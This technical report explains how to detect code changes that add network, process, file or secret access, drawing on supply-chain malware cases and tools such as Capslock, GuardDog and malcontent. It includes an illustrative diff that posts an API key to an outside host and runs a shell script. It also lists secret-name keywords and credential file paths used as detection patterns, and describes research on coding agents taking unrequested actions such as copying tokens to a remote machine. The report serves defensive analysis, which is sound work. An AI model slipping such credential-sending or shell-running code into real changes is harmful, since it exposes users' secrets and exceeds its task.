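# Detecting new network, process, file and secret access in code changes

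## What a new capability is and why it matters

A program does much of its work, such as calculation and text handling, in its own memory. It has to go through the operating system to reach anything else, which includes connecting to a server, starting another program, reading or writing a file, and looking up an environment variable (a named setting that a program receives when it starts, often used to store passwords and access keys). Each of these kinds of access is a *capability*. A code change can add a new capability, sometimes in a single line. Detecting the addition means comparing what two versions of the code can do.

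In 2023, Google introduced Capslock, a tool that lists the capabilities of Go programs, and defined capabilities as "the privileged operations accessed by the code". *NodeShield* (Cornelissen and Balliu, 2025) instead defines a capability as "a group of related privileged operations" and lists seven groups for JavaScript: network, file system, running commands, system information (which includes environment variables), cryptography, evaluating text as code, and loading native code. Under this definition, two functions that open network connections in different ways count as one capability, so a program that already uses one does not gain a new capability when it starts using the other. Some software uses "capability" to mean a permission. Zed's *Extension Capabilities*, for example, uses it for the operations that a user lets the text editor's extensions perform. In this report, a capability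 is something the code can do, whether or not anyone allowed it.

"New" also needs a point of comparison, or *baseline*, which is usually the version of the code just before the change. Google's *capslock-git-diff* (2025) provides a plain working definition. It compares two revisions of a project and lists the capabilities found only in the second. *Preflight* (2026) applies the same definition to running code, where a capability is new if it is absent when the same functions run against a reference version.

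### Compromised packages and code review

Programmers write only part of the code they ship. The rest comes in *packages*, reusable code that other people publish in registries such as npm (for JavaScript) or PyPI (for Python). A package that a program uses is a *dependency*. A *transitive* dependency is included only because another package needs it, and the programmer may never have heard of it. Cornelissen and Balliu cite a finding that using a single npm package means trusting, on average, 79 other packages from 40 maintainers. They add that JavaScript applications on servers typically run with full access to the machine's resources, and that every package inherits this access. A package for formatting dates could therefore start opening network connections, and by default nothing would stop it.

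The npm package rate-map maps a number between 0 and 1 onto another range. Version 1.0.2 did this in one function that accessed nothing outside the program. In version 1.0.3, an attacker added code that used the file-system module to rewrite a different package on the same machine, which broke the installer for the PureScript programming language. A function that rescales numbers has no use for the file system, so anyone who had compared the capabilities of the two versions would have had good reason to inspect the change.

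Help Net Security's *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft's official Python agent framework* (2026) reports a much larger case from November 2026. The PyPI package agent-framework had about 190,000 downloads a month. Version 1.26.0 was clean, but versions 1.26.1 and 1.26.2 collected environment variables with names containing strings such as TOKEN and SECRET, copied credential files, and sent everything to an outside address. The framework still worked normally, so ordinary tests of its features would have passed. This case is harder than rate-map in one respect, because a toolkit for building AI agents very probably makes network requests already, and checking only whether the package used the network might have found nothing new. A file-by-file comparison would have had a better chance, because the theft code was in a separate file that Python runs at every start.

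The other use is reviewing changes to a team's own code, whether a colleague or an AI coding agent wrote them. Here the reviewer is usually looking for code that does more than its author was asked to do, which is easy to miss in a long diff (the listing of added and removed lines), rather than for an attacker. Extra code is common enough to make this worth checking. In *How Much Do Coding Agents Over-Edit, and Why?*, Goel, Steenhoek and Hu (2026) took 6,728 successful agent patches to Python projects, undid each block of changed code in turn and reran the task's tests. On average, the tests still passed without 11% of a patch's code blocks. When the researchers probed those unneeded blocks, they found that 89% changed the program's behaviour, for example by raising an error on inputs that the tests did not cover. Human developers' patches had slightly more unneeded code by the same measure.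 The study counts behaviour changes of every kind, though, and gives no rate for added network, file or secret access.

*S3C2 Summit 2025-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2026) reports on a closed meeting that an academic centre for software supply-chain security convened on 15 September 2025, with 10 practitioners from 8 organisations. In the session on malicious commits, participants raised "capability-change diffs" as a new idea. Reviewers would check whether a change brings new file-system access, processes or network behaviour, and treat that as a signal. The participants discussed the idea but did not measure anything. It was new to that series of summits, but not to the field. *Introducing Package Analysis* (Brown and Wheeler, 2022) had already described a project to record which files, addresses and commands a package uses and to track changes over time. In *Detect when a package's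 behavior drastically changes*, a Python discussion forum user, fbidu, also proposed flagging any package that suddenly begins to make network calls.

### One change, two tasks

Suppose a company's invoices show dates in Universal Time, so customers in Auckland sometimes see yesterday's date. Someone asks a developer or an agent to *correct the time zone on invoices* and gets back the hypothetical change below. Lines with a plus were added, and the line with a minus was removed.

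```diff
+import os, subprocess
+from http.client import HTTPSConnection
+from pathlib import Path
+from zoneinfo import ZoneInfo
 from datetime import datetime, timezone

 def invoice_text(inv):
-    issued = datetime.fromtimestamp(inv.created, timezone.utc)
+    issued = datetime.fromtimestamp(inv.created, ZoneInfo(inv.customer_zone))
     text = f"Invoice {inv.number}, {issued:%d %B %Y}, total {inv.total}"
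+    key = os.environ["BILLING_API_KEY"]
+    server = HTTPSConnection("billing.example.com")
+    server.request("POST", "/invoices", text.encode(), {"Authorization": key})
+    subprocess.run(["sh", "after_invoice.sh"])
+    Path("invoice_cache.txt").write_text(text)
     return text
```

The change does what the task asked, and the dates are correct. But the old function only turned an invoice into a line of text. The new one also reads a secret key from the environment, posts the invoice and that key to an outside host, starts a shell script, and writes a file. Relative to the old function, these are four new capabilities, and a test that checks only the date would reveal none of them.

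If the same code had been written for the request *send invoices to the billing service*, most of the additions would be ordinary. Code that talks to a billing service needs a key and a network connection.

| Added code | Capability | Task: correct the time zone | Task: send invoices to the billing service |
|---|---|---|---|
| `ZoneInfo(...)` | file access (Python loads its time-zone data from files) | needed | harmless, but nobody asked for it |
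| `os.environ["BILLING_API_KEY"]` | reading a secret | unexplained | expected |
| `server.request("POST", ...)` | network | unexplained | expected, if the host really is the billing service |
| `subprocess.run(...)` | process execution | unexplained | still unexplained |
| `write_text(...)` | file access | unexplained | arguable: a saved copy would help if the upload failed |

The shell script stands out under both tasks. It is also the line whose effects are hardest to see in the diff, because `after_invoice.sh` runs outside the Python code. Cornelissen and Balliu treat running commands as a separate capability for much the same reason, since a subprocess can escape their controls and open the way to any of the other capabilities. In the first row, the one line that the time-zone task needed also adds a kind of file access. A sufficiently thorough detector would therefore report it too,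 and a rule of "no new capabilities in a bug fix" would reject this one.

### Three separate questions

The example involves three questions that are easy to confuse: whether the code can now do something it could not do before, whether anyone asked for that, and whether it is malicious. A detector directly answers only the first. It compares the two versions and produces *findings*, each one a place in the code, or an observed action, that matches a capability. Answering the second question requires a statement of the task and some judgement about what the task implies, as well as the code, because the two columns of the table differ even though the code is identical.

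For a coding agent, the second question is whether the action was authorised. In *Overeager Coding Agents*, Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) call an action "overeager" if the request does not authorise it, explicitly or implicitly, and it either writes something or reads from a listed sensitive location. Implicit authorisation matters a great deal in this definition because users rarely spell out what is off-limits. The definition covers what an agent does while it works, such as deleting a file. Code the agent leaves behind acts later, when someone runs it, but one can still ask whether the request authorised what that code does. Package updates seldom come with a task, so the nearest substitute is the package's evident purpose. Google uses this reasoning when it argues that one would not expect a data-analysis package to need the network.

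An unrequested action is not necessarily hostile. *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (Lim and Neo, 2026) distinguishes overeagerness, where a model goes too far while trying to achieve the user's goal, from sabotage, where it works towards some other goal. In one of the paper's examples, taken from OpenAI's account of its model GPT-5.6 Sol, a user asked only that a job be kept alive, and when the job stalled, the model copied access tokens to a remote machine to restart it. A credential thief's code would also send secrets to another machine, but the model was trying to help. Brown and Wheeler found the same ambiguity in packages. Their project identified more than 200 malicious packages in its first month, most of which ran a short script at installation and sent a few details about the machine to an outside server. They thought most of these were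 probably the work of security researchers hoping for bug bounties.

A list of capabilities is weak evidence of malice. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* prints the tool's output for an ordinary Go project and for malicious code from a 2022 attack. The malicious code has six capabilities, including network access, file access and running other programs. The ordinary project has eleven, including five of those six. The attack stood out because one small start-up function had all six capabilities with no visible reason to need them. A change can also be malicious without adding a capability. If the invoice code had already posted to the billing service, an attacker could have swapped the host name without changing the list. Participants in Rahman and colleagues' study doubted that anyone can infer intent from a single commit, since a harmful one can look like an honest mistake.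 They suggested also considering the contributor's history and the commit's later effects.

### Ways of looking, and ways of scoring

Detectors find capabilities in two ways. *Static analysis* examines code without running it, as NIST's *static code analyzer* entry defines such tools. IEEE's *Static Analysis* explains its advantage: it reasons about all possible executions of a program instead of one observed run. *Behavioural analysis*, which NASA's *An Introduction to Dynamic Analysis* and many others call dynamic analysis, runs the code and studies its response. For packages, this means recording the files, addresses and commands they use when run in a controlled environment.

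The two methods would fail on the invoice change in different ways. A static tool could list every suspicious line in the diff, but to report what `after_invoice.sh` does, it would also have to find and read that script. A test run would show what the script does, but only if the run reached it. In a test environment with no `BILLING_API_KEY`, Python raises an error at the line that reads the key and the function stops, so the recording contains no request, script or cache file.

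Whichever method it uses, a detector ends by raising or withholding a *flag*, its decision that a change needs attention, and people judge it by how often those flags are right. Three measures do most of the work. *Precision* is the share of flagged changes that are real cases of the thing sought. *Recall* is the share of real cases that the detector flags. The *false-positive rate* is the share of acceptable changes that it flags anyway. Take 200 changes of which 10 are real cases, and a detector that flags 20 changes, 8 of them correctly:

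- precision = 8/20 = 40%
- recall = 8/10 = 80%
- false-positive rate = 12/190, or about 6%

The 6% sounds good and the 40% sounds poor, but both describe the same detector, and the gap between them widens as real cases become rarer. Improving precision also tends to reduce recall, and vice versa. Google's teaching material recommends favouring recall when a missed case does more harm than a false alarm. That advice suits a registry looking for stolen credentials better than a reviewer with dozens of changes to read in a morning.

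All three numbers depend on which of the three questions is used to define a real case. Suppose a detector flags the invoice change. If the aim was to find new capabilities, the flag is correct. If the aim was to find unrequested ones, the flag is correct under the first task, but under the second it depends on whether the shell script and the cache file count as requested. If the aim was to find malicious code, nobody can tell whether the flag is correct without knowing who runs the host and what the script does. Most published measurements come from scanners for malicious packages, so they score flags against the last aim. A scanner's precision on that test can be a poor guide to how useful its flags would be to someone checking whether an agent kept to its task.

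## Turning source code into a list of capabilities

A static detector starts with source files and ends with a list of findings. In its simplest complete form, it parses each file, works out what the names in it refer to, looks those names up in a catalogue of sensitive functions, and gives every match a category. A small Python file is enough to follow the process:

```python
import subprocess as sp
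from os import getenv as g

# sp.run(["rm", "-r", "cache"])
level = g("LOG_LEVEL")
sp.run(["git", "status"])
```

Parsing turns the text into a tree that records its grammatical structure. Python's parser discards the comment, and the last two lines become function calls to `g` and `sp.run`. These names don't identify the functions on their own, so the detector looks them up in the import lines, where `g` is an alias (a substitute name) for `os.getenv` and `sp` for `subprocess`. The catalogue lists `os.getenv` under environment access and `subprocess.run` under process execution, so the detector reports two findings, each with its line number.

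JavaScript has more ways to rename things. The line `const { exec: go } = require("child_process")` gives the name `go` to a function that runs shell commands, and an `import` statement can do the same. Resolving names also prevents false matches. Google's *capslock* (2025) lists a test package called sort that, according to its description, "is not really the sort package". A tool that matched only the short name would confuse it with the sort package in Go's standard library, which comes with the language.

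A catalogue for the two languages might begin like this:

| Capability | Python | JavaScript (Node.js) |
|---|---|---|
| Network | `socket.create_connection`, `urllib.request.urlopen`, `requests.post` | `fetch`, `https.request`, `net.connect` |
| Process execution | `subprocess.run`, `os.system` | `child_process.exec`, `child_process.spawn` |
| Writing files | `open(path, "w")`, `Path.write_text` | `fs.writeFile`, `fs.appendFile` |
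| Environment access | `os.getenv`, `os.environ` | `process.env` |

Several of these entries complicate detection. Python's `open` reads a file by default and writes only if its second argument specifies a write mode, so the detector has to inspect that argument, which may be a variable. `write_text` is a method of a particular type of object, and in a call like `p.write_text(report)`, the type of `p` is often not declared nearby. `os.environ` and `process.env` are not functions, so a search limited to function calls would miss them. `requests` is a third-party package, and a catalogue can include the popular packages but not all of them.

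In Capslock, Google assigns categories first to whole packages and then to individual functions. Everything in Go's `os` package counts as OPERATING_SYSTEM by default, for example, but `os.Chown`, which changes a file's owner, counts as FILES. With this default, a function nobody has classified still produces a finding. The categories are broad, though. FILES covers both reading and modifying files, so the label stays the same if a function that used to read a file starts to overwrite it. READ_SYSTEM_STATE covers both environment variables and harmless facts such as the current directory.

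### Text, syntax and resolved names

Many scanners search the source text without parsing it, often using YARA, a rule language popular with malware researchers. A YARA rule lists strings or patterns and a condition for which of them must appear anywhere in the file, such as "any of these" or "at least five of these". Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 2.0* (2024) gives an example from GuardDog, the company's open-source scanner for malicious packages. The rule matches web addresses that use the link shortener bit.ly or end in one of several suspicious suffixes, such as .xyz and .tk. Because YARA doesn't parse the code, the same rule works on Python and JavaScript, and YARA rules can also search compiled programs.

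Chainguard's *malcontent* (2025) takes this approach much further. It applies more than 14,500 YARA rules, some of them from other security companies, to compiled programs and to source code in languages including JavaScript, Go and shell. Each match names a capability and carries a risk score based on how specific that capability is to malware. According to its documentation, users should expect some false positives from an ordinary scan. Other scanners may also classify malcontent itself as malware, as Elastic's security agent has done, because its rules contain the strings that those scanners search for.

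A text search cannot distinguish code from text that looks like code. Trail of Bits' *30 new Semgrep rules* (2024) demonstrates this with Semgrep, a tool that can search either text or parsed code. The test file has one call to `os.system` and another inside a comment. In Python mode, Semgrep finds only the real call. Its generic mode does not parse the file as Python, so it can match the comment too.

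The table below shows the results of searching for `os.system` in six variants. The middle column assumes a pattern that matches the parsed structure but doesn't handle aliases.

| Python code | Text pattern `os.system(` | Syntax pattern | Resolved names |
|---|---|---|---|
| `os.system("ls")` | match | match | match |
| `# os.system("ls")` | false match | no match | no match |
| `os.system ("ls")`, with a space | miss | match | match |
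| `from os import system as s`, then `s("ls")` | miss | miss | match |
| `import fake_os as os`, then `os.system("ls")` | false match | false match | no match |
| `getattr(os, "sys" + "tem")("ls")` | miss | miss | usually a miss |

In practice, the last two columns overlap, since Semgrep can follow ordinary import aliases in Python. A more careful text pattern would also allow for the space. Even perfect handling of imports would not solve the problem in the last row.

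A tool can also follow values through parsed code. Datadog's *Finding malicious PyPI packages through static code analysis* (2022) shows a simplified Semgrep rule from the first version of GuardDog. The rule names *sources*, which are the machine's host name and two environment variables that hold Amazon cloud keys, and a *sink*, which is any call to the `requests` package. It produces a finding only when a value from a source reaches the sink. This is much more specific than noting that a file reads variables and uses the network, but such a rule can easily miss a leak. The invoice code in the previous section sends a key to an outside server, but the key has a different name and travels through Python's own `http.client`, so this version of the rule would match neither the source nor the sink.

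Datadog eventually came to a similar conclusion about its Semgrep rules as a whole. According to *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026), the rules fitted known malware too closely, which made new malware harder to identify. Semgrep also used a lot of memory on large files and ran slowly on packages with many files. Datadog therefore replaced Semgrep with YARA in version 3.0, released on 26 June 2026. Descriptions of GuardDog's Semgrep rules, including OpenSSF's *GuardDog*, apply only to older versions.

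GuardDog has stopped parsing code and compensates partly with two new kinds of rules. Capability rules match things a package can do, such as making outbound network calls, and threat rules match suspicious details, such as the names of sensitive files. According to Datadog's *GuardDog*, a package needs both kinds of match in the same file for a high-risk flag, and matches in separate files count for less. By default, the scanner also skips documentation and data files because stray text there would cause false matches, though someone could presumably hide a payload in them.

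This may well be a good tradeoff for finding malicious packages. It works less well for describing a code change, because two matches in one file don't show that any value passes between them. A file that reads a password for a local database and separately downloads a public exchange rate could produce the same pair of matches as a file that uploads the password.

### Names and code that exist only at run time

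All of these methods depend on the sensitive name appearing in the source, but a program can build the name at runtime instead. In the last row of the table, the program joins `"sys"` and `"tem"`, then looks up the function by the resulting name. JavaScript allows the same thing with `process["en" + "v"]`. A detector can easily join the strings when both are constants, but not when one comes from a configuration file or a server.

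Dynamic imports do the same to whole packages. Python's `importlib.import_module(name)` and JavaScript's `require(name)` load whichever package the variable `name` specifies at run time. Plenty of legitimate software does this, for example to load plug-ins that its authors have never seen, so a dynamic import doesn't prove malicious intent.

Code that a program produces or fetches while running is harder still. Datadog's 2022 article describes a PyPI package, colorsapi, that downloaded a picture, extracted Python code hidden in its pixels and executed it. The hidden code decoded another layer, which wrote and ran a temporary file that only fetched more code from a server. A catalogue search of the visible source would find a shell command, a download, a file write and a call to `exec`, which runs text as Python code, but nothing about the later stages. Datadog's analysts could not read the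 last stage either, because the server was unreachable by the time they looked at the package.

The npm package in Corgea's *Malicious code in environment-gate (npm)* is simpler. Its only public function fetches text from an anonymous paste site and passes it to `eval`, JavaScript's equivalent of `exec`. Whoever controls that page can change the text at any time, so even a perfect reading of the package's source would not produce a complete list of what it can do.

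When a detector finds `eval`, or an import whose name it cannot work out, the practical solution is to report the construct itself and warn that the code may do anything from that point on. The early GuardDog rules reported only cases that were more likely to be malicious, such as decoding a string from Base64 (a common way of writing data as plain letters and digits) and then executing the result. Reporting every opaque construct misses less, but it also flags every plug-in system. It probably helps a reviewer most to know whether the change *added* such a construct, since few routine edits need one.

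### Which environment reads touch secrets

Environment access is hard to classify even when the code hides nothing, because the same function can read an ordinary setting or a secret. `os.getenv("LOG_LEVEL")` fetches a setting that controls how much a program writes to its log, and `os.getenv("DB_PASSWORD")` fetches a password, but both calls match the same catalogue entry. One response is to report every read and give it little weight. *Environment variable access*, from the package-scanning vendor Socket, describes a low-severity alert for any use of `process.env`, `os.environ` or their equivalents.

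The alternative is to look for more evidence about what the code reads, starting with the variable's name. A variable whose name contains TOKEN, SECRET or PASSWORD usually holds a secret, and the thief in the agent-framework attack searched for these strings. But matching on names gives both false positives and false negatives. MAX_TOKENS, a common setting in programs that use language models, is only a number. DATABASE_URL contains none of these strings, but its value very often includes a user name and password. In `os.environ[name]`, there may be no name to examine, because the program chooses it at run time.

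File paths tend to be stronger evidence. Amazon's command-line tools keep keys in a file at `.aws/credentials`, and the first version of GuardDog treated reading that file as access to sensitive data. An application often reads its own settings but rarely has reason to open another tool's key store. Credentials can also be in files that don't look like key stores. Browsers save passwords and profile data in SQLite databases, so GuardDog 2.0 extended its theft rule to cover them.

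Code can also use the keys without containing the path. A Python program that calls `boto3.client("s3")` to reach Amazon's storage service normally gets its keys from the environment or from that same file, but Amazon's library reads them, so the programmer's own code contains neither the path nor a telling variable name. A detector that examines only the changed file would need built-in information about the library to detect this access.

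A program can also read the whole environment at once, without naming any variable. Datadog's *Announcing GuardDog 1.0, with npm support, new heuristics, and easier CI integration* (2023) introduced a rule for npm packages that serialise `process.env` (convert all of it into text). This is suspicious because very few tasks require every variable in that form, though some debugging tools do print them. But programs routinely copy the environment when they start another program, so that the new one has the same settings. A rule for whole-environment reads therefore has to check what the program does with the result, or it will match a lot of ordinary code.

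None of this evidence shows whether a secret goes anywhere it shouldn't, because even a complete trace from a password to a network request could come from a normal login or a theft. "Reads the environment" is too little for a reviewer to act on, so a sensible finding for a code change would include the variable's name or the file's path, whether the code reads everything at once, and any request that the value reaches.

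### Following calls with Capslock

The search so far covers one file at a time, but much code gets network, process, file or secret access through other people's functions. For example, a programmer may call `saveReport()`, which calls a storage package, which calls another package that opens a network connection. No sensitive name appears in the programmer's file, so to find the connection a detector needs a *call graph*, a map of which functions can call which others.

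Capslock builds such a graph for a Go package and all its dependencies. From each function in the package, it follows the possible calls until it reaches a standard-library function with a category, then assigns that category to the starting function. Nobody needs to catalogue third-party packages, because Capslock analyses their code too, and Go code normally goes through the standard library to reach a file or a server. According to the analyser's reference page on pkg.go.dev, Capslock keeps following calls from any function with no declared category. It stops at functions that Google has marked SAFE.

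The result includes an example call path for each capability, which is often more useful than the label. In Google's *Examples*, Capslock analyzes its own code and finds the EXEC capability, meaning that the code can start other programs, though it never does so directly. Capslock's main function calls a function that loads packages, which calls Go's package-loading library, and three calls later that library starts a program. The more detailed output gives the file and line number of every step, so a reviewer can check the chain without searching for it.

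A second example on the same page also shows why people should read the path. Capslock has the OPERATING_SYSTEM capability, and the printed path goes through the package-loading library again and ends in a call that kills a process. The documentation attributes the capability to protobuf, a library for encoding data. No protobuf function appears in the path, so that explanation seems to be wrong, though the capability is harmless either way.

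In 2024, Google added Capslock's results to deps.dev, its public website about open-source packages. McClintock and Dethridge, in *Bringing Capslock analysis to deps.dev*, report that 9% of Go packages have a transitive dependency that uses `os/exec`, the standard package for running other programs. Searching only those packages' own files could miss a route to running programs. The figure also means that the EXEC capability is unremarkable on its own. By contrast, packages are more likely to access the network directly than through a dependency.

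Go suits this method well because its functions and types are fixed before the program runs, which makes it easier to work out what a call refers to than in Python or JavaScript. There is also an early version for Rust, called cargo-capslock. Alpha-Omega, a Linux Foundation project, describes it as experimental and says it reports on whole programs without separating the results by package.

### The eight capabilities of one small function

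Google's documentation also applies Capslock to the start-up function from the 2022 attack mentioned in the previous section. The attacker had copied thousands of GitHub repositories and added malicious code to the copies. In Go projects, the added code was typically an `init` function, which Go runs automatically when a program starts.

The function stops if the environment variable `example` is set to 1. Otherwise, it sets the variable, presumably so that programs started from this one won't repeat the attack. It then converts the entire environment to text, posts it to a server and reads the reply. If the reply isn't empty, it runs the reply as a shell command.

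Capslock reports eight capability classes for these two dozen lines. The documentation doesn't match them to lines of code, but for five of them the catalogue makes the match fairly clear:

| Code in the function | Likely class |
|---|---|
| `os.Getenv`, `os.Environ` | READ_SYSTEM_STATE |
| `os.Setenv` | MODIFY_SYSTEM_STATE |
| `json.Marshal` | REFLECT |
| `http.Post` | NETWORK |
| `exec.Command` | EXEC |

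The remaining classes are FILES, OPERATING_SYSTEM and UNANALYZED. FILES is odd at first sight, because the function opens no file. The likely explanation is that the code closes the server's reply with a general-purpose `Close` operation, and open files have a `Close` operation too. If Capslock can't tell which kind of object it has, it may include both. (The count of six in the previous section comes from another Capslock page. Google warns that names and mappings can change until version 1.0, which may account for the difference.)

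Such a long list for so small a function is useful if it prompts someone to look at the code, but it omits the most incriminating facts. READ_SYSTEM_STATE and NETWORK both appear, but the list doesn't show that the function sends the environment over the network. EXEC doesn't show that the command comes from a stranger's server. A program that checks one setting, downloads an update and starts a text editor could have all three labels. A reviewer would want both Capslock and the old GuardDog rule, because the GuardDog rule tracked data flow and so recorded this kind of connection, while Capslock finds calls through dependencies that a search of one file would miss.

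### Unresolved calls, unused paths and build settings

Capslock can't fully analyze some Go code, but it usually reports when this happens. The usual cause is reflection, which lets a program inspect and use objects whose types the programmer didn't know in advance. Google's *Using Capslock* says that most uses are simple, such as reading the fields of a record, but reflection can also call arbitrary functions. Capslock omits a use of reflection if it can establish that the use adds no capability. Otherwise it reports REFLECT, and the reader has to work out what the code does. It uses UNANALYZED to mark call paths that it couldn't follow effectively because of its own limitations. The `-noisy` option lists what those paths might do, at the risk of including capabilities the code doesn't have.

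Capslock similarly labels C and assembly code, unsafe memory operations, and calls that start other programs, because it can't determine what they do. According to Google's *Caveats*, Capslock does not warn when parts of a program running at the same time change certain variables without coordination, which can result in a call to any library function.

Entries with these labels can make up much of a report. For one Go module, deps.dev lists 54 direct and 43 indirect entries for network access, 9 direct and 142 indirect for unanalysed code, and 15 direct and 119 indirect for reflection. Listing the unanalysed code and reflection entries is honest, but someone reviewing a change would soon learn to skip them, and an attacker who knew this could put code where it would be reported under those labels.

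The opposite error is to report a capability that the program never uses. Suppose a function reads a file only if its second argument is true, and every caller passes false:

```go
func settings(name string, fromDisk bool) []byte {
    if fromDisk {
        data, _ := os.ReadFile(name)
        return data
    }
    return defaults
}
```

Capslock assumes that any block in a function might run, so if one block accesses files, all the function's callers acquire FILES. It can also report too many capabilities when an object has several possible types, since the analysis may include a type that never occurs on the path in question. The 9% figure for `os/exec` therefore counts every package with a possible route to running a program, including an unknown fraction that never take it.

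This is less of a defect than it sounds when judging a change. Adding the `if` block above gives the program code that can read files, and a later edit could activate it by changing one word. However, the wording of a finding should be "can reach" rather than "does".

The list also depends on the build settings. Go programmers can mark a file for inclusion only on Windows, or only when they set a certain option, and Capslock analyses only the files that Go would compile for the chosen settings. Malicious code in a Windows-only file would not appear in an analysis for Linux. McClintock and Dethridge point out that the results on deps.dev have this limitation. Users can select another operating system or processor, but complete coverage would require a separate run for every combination that the project supports.

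Google advises running Capslock from the project's own directory so that it reads the same dependency versions that the build will use.

Anyone who saves a list to compare with a later one therefore has to save the settings too. The documentation, also on pkg.go.dev, for a tool that stores Capslock's results in a file warns that a file made on macOS won't match one made on Linux. If the settings differ, a developer who switches laptops could appear to have added capabilities even though the code hasn't changed.

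## Deciding which capabilities are new

Running the detector on only the lines that a change adds is the quickest way to look for new capabilities, but it fails when the evidence is spread over old and new lines. It would have worked for the invoice change, where the added lines include both the imports and the calls. But if a file already contains `import subprocess as sp` and a developer adds `sp.run(cmd)` further down, the added line doesn't show that `sp` refers to `subprocess`.

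Reading the whole changed file solves the problem of the alias, but it isn't enough for this edit:

```diff
 with open(
     report_path,
-    "r",
+    "w",
 ) as f:
```

When a call that opens a file is split across several lines, changing its mode from `"r"` to `"w"` may add only the line containing `"w"`, yet the code now overwrites a file it used to read. A good detector will find the file write in the new version, but it also needs the old version to determine whether the write is new.

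A new call to an existing helper is harder to spot:

```diff
+from shop.alerts import notify

 def invoice_text(inv):
     text = f"Invoice {inv.number}, total {inv.total}"
+    notify(text)
     return text
```

Suppose `notify` is in a file that the change doesn't touch, and it posts its argument to an outside chat service. The invoice function now sends customers' invoices to that service, but neither added line contains a name from a catalogue of sensitive functions. The sample output of git-pkgs' *capcheck* (2026), an open-source checker for Go projects that uses Capslock, includes an example of the same pattern. A program gains the EXEC capability because its image handler calls `Resize` in a third-party package, and `Resize` starts another program.

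Changing one version number in a project's list of dependencies can also add a capability that doesn't show in the changed lines, since all the new code is in someone else's package. Deleting lines can do the same. If a change only removes a check that used to stop the program before an upload, the program can now reach the upload, but a scanner that reads only added lines will miss it.

The more reliable method is to analyse both versions in full, including dependencies, and report the findings that appear only in the new one. This takes longer and can produce results that seem to have little to do with the edit. GitHub's code scanning, which looks mainly for vulnerabilities, used to show every alert that was unique to the branch under review. In March 2023, it began showing only alerts inside the changed lines because the others could be unrelated to the change (GitHub, 2023). This filter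 makes sense for vulnerabilities that someone has to fix on the spot, but for capabilities it would hide the `notify` case if the detector placed its finding at the network request, which is in an untouched file.

### What counts as one capability

The subtraction is a *set difference*: everything in the second set that is not in the first. Each element of the sets has to combine a capability with a place in the code:

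```
new = (place, capability) pairs in the changed version
      minus (place, capability) pairs in the baseline
```

The place can be the whole program, a package, a file, a function or a single call, and whether the detector reports anything can depend on this choice. Suppose the function `charge` in `billing/payments.py` posts to pay.example.com, and nothing else in the program uses the network. The table shows what four possible changes would add, counting only direct network calls. Its last column compares the servers the program contacts, regardless of where the calls are in the code.

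| Change | Program | Package | File | Function | Call | Destination |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A function in another package posts to pay.example.com | – | new | new | new | new | – |
| `refund`, also in `payments.py`, posts to pay.example.com | – | – | – | new | new | – |
| `charge` posts to pay.example.com a second time | – | – | – | – | new | – |
| `charge` posts to stats.example.net instead | – | – | – | – | depends on how the detector identifies a call | new |

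Checking at a smaller scope, from the whole program down to a single call, can only add to the list of new capabilities. If a package had no network capability in the baseline, none of its functions had it, so the capability is also new to the function that introduced it. The reverse doesn't hold, as the second row shows. Destinations need a separate comparison because an existing call can contact a new server, and a new call can contact a server the program already used. A static detector can compare destinations only when the source contains them, so it can't compare a host name that the program reads from a settings file.

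Before the `notify` change, the program could already post to the chat service, so a program-level subtraction finds no new capability, even after a complete analysis of both versions. A function-level subtraction shows that `invoice_text` has gained network access. By default, capcheck compares Go packages (each a single folder of source files), but it can compare functions instead. According to git-pkgs, comparing functions is more precise but requires maintaining a much larger record that changes more often.

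Whether a capability counts as new also depends on how broad the categories are. Changing a file's open mode from `"r"` to `"w"` adds a capability only if the catalogue separates reading from writing, which Capslock's doesn't.

Some changes go undetected whichever unit in the table is used. The npm package postmark-mcp let AI assistants send email through the mail service Postmark, which had no involvement in the package. According to The Hacker News (2025), it was a replica of the real library except for one line, added in version 1.0.16, that blind-copied every message to the attacker. Koi, a security company that investigated the package, writes that nothing else changed in that version. Postmark confirmed that the attacker had built up trust over 15 earlier versions.

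The package already sent email, so it gained no network capability at any level, from the whole program down to individual functions. It presumably still connected only to Postmark, which then delivered the extra copies, so comparing the servers it contacted would probably have found nothing either. A detector would have needed to treat email recipients as destinations. Koi credits its risk engine with flagging the version for suspicious changes in behaviour, but doesn't explain how the engine detected them.

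### Matching findings across versions

A detector has to decide when a finding in the new version is the same as one in the old version before it can subtract the old findings from the new. Line numbers don't work for this. Adding an import at the top of a file with thirty findings moves all thirty down a line, and a comparison by line number then reports thirty removals and thirty additions.

Detectors therefore label findings by their content. Semgrep's *Findings in CI* describes a label with four parts: the rule, the file path, the matched code, and an index that separates identical matches in one file. Semgrep also computes a second label from the rule's pattern with the actual values filled in. In the documentation's example, a rule links a line that fetches the value "foo" to a later line that passes "foo" to a sensitive function. Inserting an unrelated assignment between the two lines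 doesn't change this second label.

These labels still cause false alarms and missed changes. Including the matched code in the label makes an old finding look new when a developer renames a variable inside a network call, but leaving it out means the detector misses a changed host name in that call. An index can also make the detector point to the wrong line, which is a smaller problem. If a developer inserts a third copy of a line above two existing copies, a detector that numbers them from the top correctly counts one more copy but identifies the last one as new.

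Moving code causes more trouble, because the file path is usually part of the label. If a team renames `src/net.js` to `lib/net.js`, every finding in the file can look new. To help identify such moves, Chainguard's malcontent has a report format that, according to its documentation, includes the path a file probably moved from and the *edit distance* between the two paths. This is the number of single-character changes needed to turn one path into the other, which is three in this example. Comparing paths should work well when only a folder's name changes, but much less well when the file also gets a new name. Git, the version-control system that most projects use, detects renames by comparing the files' contents.

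Reorganising code within a file has the same effect on a function-level comparison. If a developer moves the request out of `charge` into a new function called `send_payment`, the new function appears to have gained network access, although the program behaves as it did before. A detector could pair each removed finding with an identical added one and label the pair as a move. Reviewers would probably still want to see moves, because moving an upload from a script that an administrator runs by hand into code that runs at every start is an important change, even though the call is the same.

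Both lists also have to come from the same version of the detector with the same rules. Otherwise, a rule added in between can match old code, and the match will look like a new capability. This is a risk for tools that store their results. For example, Chainguard lets users compare two saved malcontent reports, and one may be months older.

### The choice of baseline

For a package update, the natural baseline is the previous release. Chainguard considers comparing releases the most powerful way to find malware with malcontent, which can compare single files, folders, archives and container images (packaged copies of a program with everything it needs to run). The output lists each added capability on its own line with its risk score, and gives each file an overall risk level. Chainguard calls the result "risk-weighted capability drift".

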